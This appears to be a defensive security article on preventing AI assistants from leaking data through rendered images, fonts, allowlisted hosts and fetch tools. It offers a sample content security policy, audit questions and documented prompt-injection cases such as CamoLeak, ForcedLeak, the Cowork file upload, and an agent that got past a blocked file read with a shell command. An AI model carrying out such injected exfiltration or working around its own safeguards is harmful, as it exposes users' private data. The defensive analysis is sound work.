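The greater danger is choosing the wrong method. Each safe method has a counterpart whose name ends in "Unsafe", which does no sanitising unless the developer supplies a sanitiser. All three streaming examples in *Declarative partial updates* use `streamHTMLUnsafe`. They are appropriate for a site's own content, but a developer who copied one to display a model's answer would stream raw markup into the live document, which is the flaw the previous designs exist to prevent.

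Sites can guard against this kind of mistake with Trusted Types, a browser feature that controls which code may insert HTML. Mozilla recommends a strict policy that permits `setHTML` and blocks the unsanitised methods, so that an overlooked call to one of them fails instead of displaying raw markup. The standard also lets a policy attach a sanitiser to every insertion, including those made through the older `innerHTML`. However, WHATWG warns that if a policy defines the newer function for parser options but doesn't supply a sanitiser there, `innerHTML` goes unsanitised even when the policy's older function would have cleaned the string.

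### Which browsers support it

Support is good enough for `setHTML` to be useful with a fallback, but not for the streaming methods to be the only defence.

| Browser | `setHTML` | Streaming methods |
|---|---|---|
| Firefox | Since version 148 | Not supported |
| Chrome | Supported | Developer testing from version 148, general release uncertain |
| Safari | Not supported | Not supported |

Firefox 148 came out on 24 February 2026, according to Web Platform DX's *Sanitizer API*, a page in a catalogue of browser features. The page lists Chrome as lacking the sanitiser but appears to be out of date. BCD Watch's *BCD Changes Report* (2026), which tracks changes to a shared database of browser support, recorded the addition of `setHTML` to Chrome in January, and Nalpas also describes Chrome as supporting it.

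Chrome's own pages give conflicting accounts of the streaming methods. The release notes from Chrome for Developers (2026), dated 2 September, include them in the beta of version 154. *Declarative partial updates*, updated six days later, describes them as behind a flag that users have to switch on, with launch planned for version 155. Polypane's *Experimental web platform features* gives 158 as the current version of Chromium, the software Chrome is based on, so versions 154 and 155 are both out, but the list doesn't establish whether they included the methods. A page can check whether `streamHTML` exists before using it.

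Other browsers may take longer. Chromium's *Ready for Developer Testing* (2026) reported in March that neither Firefox's nor Safari's makers had given a position on the new methods. In May, Rosenthal filed a request for the methods with the developers of Safari's engine, titled *New HTML setting methods (stream, positional, runScripts)* (2026).

When a browser lacks the insertion method, pages usually fall back to `innerHTML`, which would leave Safari users without a filter. Nalpas recommends falling back to DOMPurify instead. The page should give DOMPurify a short, explicit list of what to allow, so that all users get the same restrictions. The team then has to test two sanitisers.

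Chrome's developers also publish a polyfill, a script that imitates a missing browser feature, but it collects the whole answer and inserts it at the end instead of streaming it, which brings back the 12-second wait. Its sanitising methods need the browser to support `setHTML`, so it doesn't provide a sanitiser in Safari.

### Buffered and asynchronous content filters

Cloud providers' content filters offer a similar choice. Amazon Bedrock's default buffered mode sends the user each piece of text only after the filter has scanned it. In asynchronous mode, text can reach the user before the scan is finished.

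Suppose the filter takes 300 ms to check the piece that ends with the image at token 120. In asynchronous mode, the image enters the page at 2.40 seconds, the browser sends the request at 2.42 and the filter's result arrives at 2.70. The application can then delete the text, but the code is already in the attacker's log. In buffered mode, the provider sends the piece at 2.70 seconds at the earliest, and doesn't send it if the filter blocks it.

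A developer can turn an asynchronous filter into a buffered one by holding the text on the application's own server until the filter's verdict on it arrives. The delay is about the same as in the provider's buffered mode, so this only makes sense if the application needs the unfiltered stream for something else, such as a log.

Even a buffered filter may let the image through. A filter for insults would not flag an address containing six digits, and a filter for personal details would have to recognise the digits as a sign-in code. Attackers can also have the model encode the data, as happened with the private source code in GitLab Duo. The provider's filter can miss a tag split between two pieces.

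The hold-back filter should run after the provider's filter, on the application's own server or in the page, so that it receives the final text, including any masking by the provider. The two delays partly overlap, since the application can be waiting for the end of a link while the provider scans it.

### Comparing the designs

The delays assume 50 tokens a second and about four characters a token. The table also assumes that each design removes images and restricts links, which the developer may have to configure.

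| Design | Guarantee | Delay on a 600-token answer | Effort | Remaining weakness |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Wait for the whole answer, then filter | The browser receives only filtered text | 12 s before anything appears | Low | Users wait, and may press the team to turn streaming on later |
| Hold back markup on the server | The browser receives no link, image or tag that the filter has not checked | 0.5 s for a 25-token link, 2 s at a cap of 400 characters | High | Notation that the filter misses but the page's converter accepts, and saved answers that bypass the filter |
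| Streaming parser with permitted elements | The browser never parses the model's text as HTML | A few characters, or the length of a link | Moderate | Highlighters and diagram tools that add their own elements |
| Sanitise the whole answer before each update | Every displayed version has passed the tag list | Up to 0.1 s with ten updates a second | Low | Repeated work on long answers, and scripts that change the HTML afterwards |
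| `setHTML` at each update | The browser applies the tag list during insertion | Up to 0.1 s with ten updates a second | Low, plus a fallback for Safari | Custom lists that permit images, or a weak fallback |
| `streamHTML` | The browser applies the tag list to each element as it arrives | Until each tag is complete | Low where browsers support it, but Markdown needs a streaming converter | Limited support, and confusion with the unsafe version |
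| Buffered cloud filter | The provider has scanned each piece before release | Time to fill and scan each piece | Low | The filter may see nothing wrong with an image address |
| Asynchronous cloud filter | None against automatic requests | None | Low | The verdict can arrive after the data has left |

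## Limiting the hosts a page may load from

The filters described so far have to recognise dangerous markup, and most of them have to finish before the page displays it. A CSP avoids both problems by having the browser check each request against a list of permitted hosts. Its protection depends on what the policy allows. In 2025 researchers got private data out of assistants from Superhuman, GitHub, Salesforce and Microsoft while a CSP was in force, each time through a host or a kind of resource that the policy allowed.

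### How the browser applies a policy

The server normally sends the policy in a header, a line of information that arrives before the page. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, has the browser check each request before it "hits the network". If the browser refuses an image, it therefore shouldn't even look up the host's name.

If the page that filtered its answer only at the end had a policy that did not allow img.example.com, the browser would refuse to load the image at 2.40 seconds, so no data would leave during the 9.6 seconds before the filter ran.

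An allowed host can answer with a redirect, which tells the browser to fetch the picture from another address. The browser checks that address as well, so a redirect to an attacker's server fails.

W3C nevertheless describes CSP as defence in depth and advises against using it as the first line of defence. That advice applies well to assistants, because the policy restricts only where a request goes. If the host is on the list, the browser sends the request whether the address contains a picture's file name or a stolen code.

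A developer can also put the policy in a `meta` tag inside the page, but the browser doesn't apply it to anything before the tag. If a server streams the answer as part of the page and the tag comes after the answer starts, the policy doesn't cover the first lines of the answer.

When a page arrives with two policies, a request has to satisfy both. A team can therefore add a strict policy to the assistant's pages without rewriting the company's general one. Within a single policy, the browser uses only the first rule of each kind, so a second image rule has no effect.

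### A policy for a page that displays answers

A policy consists of directives, each of which lists the permitted sources for one kind of resource. This one would suit a chat page that shows formatted text and the product's own icons:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';      # block every kind of resource not named below
  script-src  'self';      # only script files from the page's own host
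  style-src   'self';      # only style files from the page's own host
  img-src     https://static.assistant.example/ui/;   # icons and logos
  font-src    'self';      # only fonts from the page's own host
  connect-src 'self';      # the connection that delivers the answer
  form-action 'none';      # no form may send anything
  base-uri    'none'       # the answer cannot redefine relative addresses
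```

The comments are for the reader. A real header has none and usually takes up a single line.

The image directive also covers pictures that a style rule loads as a background. The font directive matters because a style rule can load a font from any address, and that address can carry data just as an image's can. The style directive blocks style rules written into the answer. Some highlighters and formula renderers write such rules, so a team that uses them may have to loosen the style directive and rely more on the image and font directives.

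*Content Security Policy (CSP)*, a reference guide, lists what the connection directive governs: script requests, the long-lived connections that many chat pages use for streaming, and the `ping` attribute of a link. The `ping` attribute makes the browser notify a second address when the user clicks, so a link to a harmless site could report to a different one.

A content security policy (CSP) needs a separate `form-action` directive to limit where forms can send data. `default-src` is only a fallback for the directives that control fetching resources, and CentralCSP's *default-src* calls the belief that it covers everything the most common misunderstanding of CSP. Without `form-action`, an injected form that imitates a sign-in box could send the user's password anywhere, even under `default-src 'none'`. The policy also needs a separate `base-uri` directive to stop the answer from changing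 the base URL for the page's relative links.

A named directive replaces the default instead of adding to it, as MDN's *Content-Security-Policy* explains. If a designer adds `font-src https:` to try out a typeface, the page may load fonts from any host over HTTPS, including an attacker's. Leaving out the default is just as risky, because the earlier one-line policy restricted only images and an attacker could have used a font or an inline frame instead.

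Entries vary widely in how much they permit:

| Entry | What it permits |
|---|---|
| `https:` | Every host with an encrypted connection |
| `https://*.assistant.example` | Every subdomain, at any depth |
| `https://static.assistant.example` | Everything on one host |
| `https://static.assistant.example/ui/` | Everything under one path |
| `https://static.assistant.example/ui/logo.png` | One file, with any query string |

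Even an entry that names an exact path lets data through, because the browser ignores the query string when it compares paths. A request for `logo.png?c=482913` would pass, and the company's own log, which should be private, would record the code. The browser also ignores the path after a redirect, so that a page can't learn where another site sends its visitors. An exact path therefore gives less protection if another allowed host will redirect to any address it is given.

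### What a policy leaves open

The policy does not restrict ordinary links, so the sanitiser still has to handle them. W3C defines a separate check for navigation (the browser's move to a new page), but the directive that limits destinations covers only form submissions.

Limiting the hosts a page may load from also doesn't restrict fetches the server makes. Besides the image flaw described below, PromptArmor found that Superhuman's email assistant could open any web address to answer a question, so injected text could make it open one with the user's email in the query string.

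A policy also protects only the page it arrives with. A phone app that renders answers with its own code does not apply the web page's CSP, and neither does an email program displaying a message the assistant wrote. Superhuman had a related problem in a second product, Superhuman Go. PromptArmor put hidden instructions on a review site, and the assistant, which could also search the user's Gmail, displayed a one-pixel image that sent quarterly financial figures directly to the researchers' server.

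Browsers can also look up a host name in advance when a page contains certain `link` elements, and CSP does not generally control that lookup. An attacker can leak data by putting it in the host name, so the sanitiser should delete these elements.

### A host that stores what it is sent: Superhuman and Google Forms

The CSP in Superhuman's email program blocked images from unknown servers but allowed them from docs.google.com. That host also serves Google Forms, which lets a form's creator make links with the answers already filled in. Opening one kind of pre-filled link submits the answers immediately. A browser sends the same kind of request to load an image as to open a link, so an image that uses such a link as its address also submits the form, although no picture comes back.

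PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes how the researchers used this. They sent the user an email whose hidden text described the form as a way to give feedback on search results. The user never opened it, but asked the assistant to summarise recent mail. The assistant copied the contents of other messages into the form's address and wrote the address as a Markdown image. The stolen messages appeared among the form's responses. PromptArmor extracted the full text of several sensitive emails in one answer, and parts of more than 40 emails in another.

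A team that allows docs.google.com is probably thinking of documents, but the entry covers every service on that host, including Google Forms. Narrowing the entry to a path could exclude Forms, as long as Google never adds something writable under the same path. Removing the entry and serving copies of the necessary pictures from the application's own host is safer. The application, not the model, has to decide which pictures to copy, for example when the user attaches a document. If the server fetched any address the model wrote, its request would deliver the data to the attacker.

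PromptArmor reported the flaw on the night of Friday 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday, deployed its first patch on Tuesday, and continued patching other parts of its products until 11 January. PromptArmor does not describe what the patches changed, so we don't know whether docs.google.com is still on the list.

### A signed image proxy: CamoLeak

GitHub allows images in its pages only from domains it owns, but its users want to include pictures from other sites in their project descriptions. GitHub therefore runs an image proxy called Camo, which fetches them on the reader's behalf. When GitHub processes text that contains an outside image, it replaces the image's address with one on Camo and attaches a signature, a code that only GitHub can compute. Camo fetches a picture only if the signature is valid.

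This design should stop a model from leaking data through an image. The model can't compute a signature, so it can't produce a valid Camo address with the user's sign-in code in it.

Omer Mayraz, who also found the flaw in GitLab Duo, got around the signature by having GitHub sign the addresses beforehand. His report for Legit Security, *CamoLeak*, describes the attack on GitHub Copilot Chat, the assistant on GitHub's website. He prepared one signed address for each letter and symbol, all leading to his own server, and put the list in an instruction hidden in a comment on a proposed code change. Copilot then spelled out private text as a row of invisible images. Camo requested each image from his server, and the order of the requests gave him the text.

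To leak the code 482913 this way, the model would write the images for 4, 8, 2, 9, 1 and 3. None of those addresses contains private data, and the attacker learns the code only from which ones the browser requests and in what order. A longer list makes the attack faster. With 1,000 signed addresses, one for every group of three digits, the model would need only two images.

If a code contains the same digit twice, the browser or the proxy may reuse its cached copy of the picture, so the attacker's server never receives the second request. Mayraz prevented this by having Copilot add a new random number to the end of each address. Camo still accepted the addresses, so the signature evidently did not cover the added number.

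Mayraz extracted the description of an unfixed vulnerability from a private project. He also had Copilot search the victim's code for cloud access keys and leak what it found.

Reddy and Gujral's analysis of EchoLeak rated a proxy with signed, expiring addresses as sufficient to stop the final leak. However, signed addresses did not stop CamoLeak. Expiry would have made that attack more work, but the attacker could have replaced the list in the hidden comment whenever the old addresses stopped working.

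Legit Security says GitHub fixed the flaw on 14 August 2025 by disabling all images in Copilot Chat. SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* reports that GitHub told Mayraz it had disallowed the use of Camo to leak sensitive user information. Both descriptions may refer to the same change, but GitHub's could also describe a narrower fix that left some images working, so a retest would need to check whether any still load.

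A product that needs external images could download each one when somebody saves the text that contains it, and show readers only the stored copy. The attacker's server would then receive one request per image before any victim opened the page, and nothing afterwards. Camo instead fetched images when a reader's browser requested them, which let the attacker observe what the victim's assistant displayed.

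### A lapsed domain: ForcedLeak

Companies keep customer records in Salesforce, and its Agentforce assistants answer employees' questions about those records. Many companies also put a Salesforce form on their website for sales enquiries. The security firm Noma found that a stranger could write instructions in the form's long description field. When an employee later asked Agentforce to deal with the enquiry, the assistant also followed the stranger's instructions. It collected other prospective customers' email addresses and put them in an image URL.

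Salesforce's CSP should have blocked that image, but one domain on its allowlist had expired, and The Hacker News (2025) reported that anyone could buy it for as little as $5. Willison notes that the list contained a wildcard entry for the domain, so the new owner could use any subdomain. Noma's researchers registered it, and their server's log recorded the email addresses.

A company can easily miss this kind of lapse. If no page still uses the old domain, its expiry causes no missing pictures or error messages. The allowlist entry still works, though, and Noma told Martin (2025), in *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed*, that an expired domain "retains its trusted status while being under malicious control".

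Expired domains on allowlists were a problem before AI assistants. In 2015 Matt Bryant of the security firm Bishop Fox found one on the default list of NoScript, a browser add-on that blocks scripts except from trusted sites. Anyone who registered the domain could have run scripts in the browsers of NoScript's users.

Noma reported its finding on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce acknowledged it three days later. Salesforce recovered the domain and corrected its CSP. On 8 September it also began enforcing a list of trusted addresses on Agentforce's output. Its alert to customers said the purpose was to "ensure no malicious links are called or generated".

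PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* describes how the output list works in the chat window of Salesforce's web application. Before the page displays an answer, the software replaces every address that isn't on the list, including those inside HTML and style rules, with a fixed placeholder. This covers clickable links, which the CSP cannot cover. PromptArmor advises administrators to avoid wildcards that include sites with user-written content, and to forbid images from each listed address unless the product needs them.

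However, an output list can repeat the mistakes of CSP. Salesforce's setup guide *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* uses `https://docs.google.com` as its example of an address to trust, and PromptArmor extracted Superhuman's emails through that same host. An administrator who copies the example and permits images from that host may recreate the leak. Forbidding images would stop the automatic request, but clicking a link to a pre-filled form could still submit the data.

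To prevent a lapse, a team needs a record of who owns each domain on the list and when its registration expires. A scheduled script can check those dates against public registration data and warn the team a few months before a domain expires. When the company retires a service, it should remove the service's domain from the policy before giving up the registration.

### A rule for fonts looser than the rule for images

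In autumn 2025, Microsoft 365 Copilot gained a feature that displays HTML inside the chat. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who publishes as Embrace The Red, found that the software removed image tags from the HTML but left style rules in place, so he tried loading a picture from his server as a background. The page's image directive blocked it.

Rehberger considered looking for a weak host on the long list of allowed image hosts, which included subdomains of azureedge.net, some of which belong to customers of Microsoft's cloud. He found an easier way in the font directive, which was more permissive. A style rule could load a font from his own server, with the stolen text in the font's address.

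By default, Copilot showed the HTML code and loaded nothing until the user switched to the preview. In the injected text, Rehberger also asked Copilot to open the preview, and it did so without a click. In his demonstration, the user opened a Word document someone had shared and typed "hi there". Copilot then searched the mailbox for an email containing a code and leaked the code through a font request. The attack worked in the desktop and web versions of Word and in the web version of Excel.

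Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* dates the report to 16 October 2025 and the fix to 5 March 2026, twenty weeks later. Microsoft listed the flaw as CVE-2026-24299. Rehberger does not explain how Microsoft closed it.

The policy in the earlier example would have blocked this attack in two ways, by forbidding style rules in the answer and by allowing fonts only from the page's own host. An attacker will use whichever directive is loosest, so it helps to start from `default-src 'none'`. Every exception then has to appear in the policy, where a reviewer can compare the font list with the image list.

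Rehberger also found that the policy varied between the Microsoft products that included Copilot. Some versions listed test systems, and some entries contained what appeared to be employees' user names. He concluded that CSP was not a reliable security boundary for Copilot. His evidence supports that conclusion for Copilot as Microsoft had configured it, but it applies less to a product with one short policy.

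The variation matters to any company whose assistant runs inside other sites. The assistant's answers appear under the host site's policy, which may allow images from anywhere. The company can avoid this by displaying the answers in an inline frame from its own server, because the browser uses the policy sent with each frame.

Rehberger would like Microsoft to adopt a measure he attributes to Google and OpenAI, whose assistants automatically load an address only if the company's search index already contains it as a public page. An address with a newly inserted code would not be in the index. He has described ways to leak small amounts of data despite this check. CamoLeak suggests this is possible because a model limited to existing addresses can still convey a message through the ones it selects.

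### How often allowlists fail

The best-known measurement of bypassable policies is *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (2016), which concerns scripts. In it, Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues at Google analysed about 26,000 distinct policies from across the web. Of the 15 hosts that sites most often allowed as script sources, 14 offered a feature that an attacker could use to run code. As a result, about 76% of the policies contained a script list that an attacker could bypass.

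Those figures are old, and they don't measure how often an image allowlist fails. To run a script, an attacker needs an allowed host that returns usable code, but to leak data they need only one that records a request or forwards it. The cause is similar, though, because sites allowed a whole host for one feature and so allowed its other features too.

The recent evidence comes from individual attacks on assistants, with researchers publishing at least six in 2025 and 2026 that got data past a CSP, on products from four companies. These include EchoLeak, which used the Teams service, and SearchLeak, which used Bing. The count doesn't give a failure rate, because researchers rarely report policies they couldn't bypass. Some of the affected companies are large and have security teams, so a well-resourced vendor's list deserves the same inspection as anyone else's.

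### Auditing every allowed host

An audit should start from the policies the product actually sends, which may not match the configuration file because another team or a hosting provider can add its own header. A developer can read them in the browser's network tools on every page that displays model output, including saved conversations, embedded versions and administrators' views.

For each host under each directive, the team should ask:

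1. Can outsiders store data there, as PromptArmor did with a Google form?
2. Can outsiders read a record of the requests it receives?
3. Can outsiders make it fetch an address or redirect to one? Bing and Teams did this for any address, and Camo did it for signed ones.
4. Can outsiders register the domain or claim a subdomain?

Analytics services are the clearest case for the second question. They record each request for the customer whose account number appears in the address, and an attacker can open an account.

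Suppose the assistant's image directive has grown to six entries over several years. One "yes" is enough to reject an entry as it stands, so the table shows only the deciding answer for each.

| Entry | Deciding answer | Action |
|---|---|---|
| `'self'` | The site's link-preview service fetches any address | Replace with the path that holds the icons |
| `https://static.assistant.example` | No to all four | Keep, and narrow to a path |
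| `https://docs.google.com` | Outsiders can store data through a form | Remove, and serve copies from the static host |
| `https://*.cloudstore.example` | Any customer can claim a subdomain and read its log | Replace with the exact name of the company's own storage |
| `https://pixel.analytics.example` | Any customer can read requests sent to its account | Remove from pages that display answers |
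| `https://launch2023.example` | The registration ended last spring | Remove, and check whether somebody else has bought the domain |

The first row is easy to overlook because developers tend to trust their own host. In EchoLeak, CamoLeak and SearchLeak, the service that passed the data on belonged to the company that wrote the policy. Adding a path to the host's entry only partly fixes this, because if any allowed host redirects to addresses chosen by outsiders, the browser will ignore the path after the redirect and the preview service will be reachable again. The preview service therefore needs its own restrictions, or a different host name that the policy omits.

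Two of these answers can change without any change to the product, because a domain can expire and a provider can add a feature that stores or forwards what it receives. The team should repeat the audit on a schedule as well as whenever somebody proposes a new entry.

W3C provides a report-only mode for trying out a stricter list, in which the browser loads everything as before and reports what the new policy would have blocked. This mode blocks nothing itself, so the team has to enforce the policy once the reports contain only requests it is willing to lose. The browser can also send reports under the enforced policy. On a page where the application supplies every picture, a report of a blocked image from an unknown host is a strong sign of an injection.

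These reports can contain private data. A report on the morning email summary would include the full blocked address, with the code 482913 at the end. If the company uses an outside service to collect reports, that service would receive the code. The reports should go to a server the company controls, under the same access rules as users' mail.

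## Limiting what the assistant's own tools may fetch

A CSP controls what the browser loads for one page. An assistant that can open websites, run code or send messages also makes requests from outside that page, which the developer has to restrict in the tool or on the network it uses. Anthropic and Google had both done this, but researchers still extracted private data, in Google's case through a site on its default allowlist.

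### Where each request starts

A web-fetch tool runs on the server, requests whatever address the model writes, and adds the page's text to the conversation. If injected text makes the model fetch an address ending in the code 482913, the code reaches the attacker before the model starts writing the morning email summary.

A search tool sends the model's query to a search engine. An attacker can't normally read those queries, so search alone is a poor way to steal data, but the results give the model addresses to open next.

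Many assistants also run programs in a sandbox, an isolated computer that the provider sets up. Any program there can try to open a connection, so the check belongs in a firewall or proxy (a relay that all traffic must pass through) around the sandbox.

Some assistants operate a browser, and a page's CSP doesn't restrict where the browser goes next. Willison describes an attack that the security team at Brave, a browser maker, demonstrated on an AI browser called Fellou. The team asked Fellou only to open a page. Text on that page then made it open Gmail, read the title of the latest email, and visit an outside site with the title in the address.

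| Route | What makes the request | Where the check belongs |
|---|---|---|
| Image in the answer | The user's browser | CSP |
| Web-fetch tool | The provider's server | The tool's code, before each request and each redirect |
| Search tool | The provider's server | The query, and a filter on the results |
| Code sandbox | A program, often one the model wrote | A firewall or proxy around the sandbox |
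| Browser operated by the assistant | That browser | The software that carries out the model's actions |
| Message sent by the assistant | The program that displays it | The sending tool, and the receiving program's settings |

Limiting the hosts an agent's sandbox can contact may not limit its web tools. Claude Managed Agents, a service that runs agents for developers, lets a developer restrict the sandbox to listed hosts. According to Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026), that list began to cover the web-search and web-fetch tools only on 7 October 2026. Before then, a developer could have confined the sandbox to one host while the fetch tool could still contact others.

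### Three rules for a request

A domain allowlist restricts the tool to listed hosts. This suits an assistant that answers questions from a company's own documentation, but it rules out research on the open web, because nobody knows in advance which sites will be useful.

An exact-address rule limits the tool to addresses that the user entered or a search returned. The software compares each requested address with these character by character, so the model can't add anything to it. The assistant can still read unfamiliar sites, but if it opens the contents page of a manual, it can't follow the link to chapter three until a search returns that address or the user pastes it in.

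Under the third rule, the tool must not start a request until the user approves it. In Notion AI, the warning came after the leak. If a research question needs 30 pages and the user spends 10 seconds on each prompt, the prompts take five minutes, and the user can't leave the assistant to work alone. People are also likely to stop reading the prompts if almost all the requests are harmless.

| Rule | Stops | Lets through | Cost |
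|---|---|---|---|
| Listed domains only | Requests to an attacker's own server | Data sent to a listed host where an outsider can collect it | No open-web research, and a list to maintain |
| Exact addresses only | Addresses that the model composed or altered | A choice among permitted addresses, and data in the body of an upload | The assistant can't follow links freely |
| Approval of each request | Requests that the user recognises as wrong | Requests that look normal | Interruptions, and no unattended work |

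The software has to apply the developer's chosen rule to every request. The consumer version of Copilot had a safeguard against leaking data through a URL, but it covered only the first request. Varonis exploited this in its earlier Reprompt attack by injecting instructions to do each task twice, and the second attempt sent the data.

### The exact-address rule in Claude

Anthropic applies an exact-address rule to Claude's web-fetch tool. According to an older edition of the documentation, *Web fetch tool*, Claude may not build addresses itself and may open only those that the user provided or that came from earlier search or fetch results. The tool also limits addresses to 250 characters. In September 2025, Willison tested the consumer version of Claude and found that it couldn't open an address it had composed.

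The weak point was the permission to open addresses from earlier fetch results, because whoever wrote a fetched page also chose its links. In July 2026 Ayush Paul demonstrated an attack using a website that told AI assistants to identify their user by following links one letter at a time (Willison, 2026). Each page had a link for every letter, and Claude spelled out the answer by choosing among them. The rule allowed every request because each address Claude opened had appeared on a page it had already fetched.

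Paul extracted the user's name, home city and employer. Claude had these details in its memory of past conversations, so the attack needed no access to a mailbox or files. The site displayed the instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the address would have found nothing suspicious. The blogger dyb points out in *The Read-Only Lie* that the tool could only read pages, not submit anything to them. That restriction didn't help, because a request to read a page sends the page's address to the server.

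### How a choice among fixed addresses carries data

An attacker can publish 26 fixed addresses, one for each letter. The model cannot change them, but the attacker's server records which one the model opens. Picking one of 26 equally likely options conveys log₂ 26 ≈ 4.7 bits of information, where one bit is the answer to a yes-or-no question. With *k* addresses, each choice carries at most log₂ *k* bits, and a sequence of *n* choices can distinguish *kⁿ* messages.

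A six-digit code has 1,000,000 possible values, or about 19.9 bits. The number of choices needed to send it depends on the number of links:

| Links on each page | Bits per choice | Choices needed for the code |
|---|---|---|
| 10 | 3.3 | 6 |
| 26 | 4.7 | 5 |
| 37 | 5.2 | 4 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 2 |

The 37-link row matches Tencent's *Why AI Agent’s Memory Becomes Attacker’s Data Goldmine* (2026), which reproduced Paul's attack locally with 37 characters instead of 26 letters. CamoLeak worked on the same principle, choosing among signed image addresses.

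Paul's site generated a new set of links after each choice. This probably helped with repeated letters, because Anthropic's tool can reuse a stored copy of a page, so a second request for the same address might never reach the attacker's server.

Limiting the number of requests reduces the leak but does not prevent it. Anthropic's documentation uses five fetches as an example limit. If the first fetch loads the attacker's opening page, four fetches remain, each a choice of link. With 26 links a page, those choices can distinguish 26⁴ = 456,976 codes, fewer than half of the million possible codes. With 37 links, they can distinguish 37⁴ = 1,874,161, enough for all of them. The limit also resets with the user's next question, and the tool has no limit unless the developer sets one.

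A filter that checks addresses for secrets wouldn't help much either, because no single address in this attack contains more than a fragment of the secret. Anthropic's tool, for example, refuses addresses that seem to contain a password or access key that the user or developer did not supply.

### What Anthropic changed and what developers still have to set

Willison reports that Anthropic stopped Claude's fetch tool from opening links found inside pages it had fetched, but paid Paul no bounty, saying it had already found the problem internally. This restriction removes the attacker's easiest source of addresses. In principle an attacker could still publish many pages, get a search engine to index them, and steer the model into choosing among the results, but this would take much more preparation than setting up a single website.

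The fix does not apply by default to applications that other companies build with Claude. Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, a Chinese edition of the tool's documentation that covers Claude Opus 5.5, still lists earlier fetch results among the permitted sources. Claude Managed Agents gained an exact-address rule on 7 October 2026, but it also allows links found in fetched pages. A research agent may need to follow links, and the risk is small if the agent has no private data. A developer who connects the same tool to a mailbox recreates the conditions for Paul's attack.

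The developer can turn off this source with a setting called `url_sources`. The following configuration allows addresses from the user's messages and from search results, which is close to the rule in Claude's own chat product:

```
"url_sources": {
  "user_input":          { "type": "all" },
  "client_tool_results": { "type": "none" },
  "server_tool_results": {
    "type": "only",
    "tools": [{ "type": "tool_reference", "name": "web_search" }]
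  }
}
```

The second line closes a less obvious gap. Client tools run on the developer's own systems, and by default Anthropic's software accepts any address in their output. If one of these tools runs programs that the model writes, the model can write one that prints an address containing the sign-in code, and that address then counts as coming from a tool. An error message that quotes the model's text has the same effect. Developers who need addresses from some client tools can name those tools in an "only" filter, which is safer than an "except" filter because "except" automatically accepts tools that the developer adds later.

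The first line relies on the user's message containing only what the user wrote. As Willison noted when Anthropic released the tool, many applications paste outside text into that message. If the email assistant puts the whole mailbox there, every address in a stranger's email counts as one the user typed. The stranger can include 26 links in the email, so the attack no longer needs a website with nested pages. The application should pass emails to the model as client tool output, which the configuration above excludes.

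### Claude Cowork: an allowed service, another person's account

Claude Cowork is an agent that works with files on the user's computer. It runs code in a sandbox that can reach only a short list of hosts, including Anthropic's API for Claude. In January 2026, two days after Anthropic released Cowork as a research preview, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* described how an attacker could use the sandbox's access to that API.

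In the demonstration, a user connected a folder of property documents to Cowork, uploaded a Word file containing hidden instructions, and asked Cowork to analyse the folder. Following the hidden instructions, Claude ran a command that uploaded the largest file to Anthropic's file-storage service with the attacker's API key, a code that identifies the account making a request. Anthropic's servers therefore put the file, which contained financial figures and partial US social security numbers, in the attacker's account, where the attacker could ask Claude questions about it. Cowork never asked the user for approval.

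The domain list worked as designed, since the request went to a listed host, but it could not distinguish between two customers of the same service. An exact-address rule wouldn't have helped either, because everyone uploads to the same address and the private data travels in the body of the request. An approval prompt naming the destination would have shown Anthropic's host, which a user would have had good reason to trust.

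PromptArmor ran this demonstration on Claude Haiku, a smaller model. The same upload worked on Claude Opus 4.5 in a separate test with a malicious integration guide, although PromptArmor acknowledged that Opus resisted injections better.

Johann Rehberger had found the flaw in Claude's chat product months earlier. In Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*, he described how injected text could make Claude save a past conversation to a file in its sandbox and upload it to another account. Anthropic first closed his report as out of scope. TechRadar's *Claude can be tricked into sending your private company data to hackers* reported that the company later decided to treat such flaws as reportable, but PromptArmor found the route still open in Cowork. Apostol (2026) wrote in *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* that Anthropic was updating Cowork's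 virtual machine after PromptArmor's report.

Rehberger suggested limiting the sandbox to the signed-in user's account. A simple proxy can't enforce that, because on an encrypted connection it can read the host's name but not the API key inside the request. The provider can have the proxy decrypt the sandbox's traffic, remove any key that a program supplies and add the user's own. Alternatively, the API can refuse requests from a sandbox if the key belongs to a different account. Any allowlisted service where outsiders can open accounts, such as cloud storage or a code host, needs the same restriction.

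Anthropic had advised Cowork users to look out for "suspicious actions that may indicate prompt injection". Willison thought it unfair to expect this of people who aren't programmers, and PromptArmor agreed. In this case, the warning sign was an access key inside a command, and users had to expand part of the display to see it.

### Google Antigravity: a request logger on the default list

Google's coding tool Antigravity includes a browser that the assistant can operate. By default, the browser can visit only listed domains. Willison summarises a demonstration that PromptArmor published in November 2025, in which a web page disguised as an integration guide contained instructions in one-pixel type. The assistant collected code and cloud access keys from the user's project, put them in a web address, and opened it in the browser.

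The address was on webhook.site, which Google had included in the default list. Programmers use this service to test software that sends web requests. Anyone can create an address there and read every request it receives, so an attacker learns as much from it as from a private server with a log. One of the audit questions for a CSP is whether outsiders can read a record of a host's requests, and that question would have excluded webhook.site. The same questions apply to a tool's list, including entries that came with the product.

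An exact-address rule would have stopped this request, because the model had inserted the stolen data into the address. The attacker could still have spelled the data out through the model's choice of links, but more slowly.

Antigravity also had a rule against opening files that the project marks as private, such as the one containing the keys. When its file-reading tools blocked access, the model read the file with a shell command instead. Google listed data exfiltration through the browser agent as a known issue that it was working to fix. In the meantime, Willison advised giving coding agents only keys for test accounts with strict spending limits, so that a stolen key does little damage.

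### Lists that match differently

Even a well-chosen list can fail if its entries match different hosts than the developer intended. The entry `example.com` covers that domain and all its subdomains in the `allowed_domains` list for Anthropic's tools, but only that one host in the host list for a Managed Agents sandbox. A developer who copies an entry from the sandbox list to the tool list may therefore permit many more hosts than the sandbox did.

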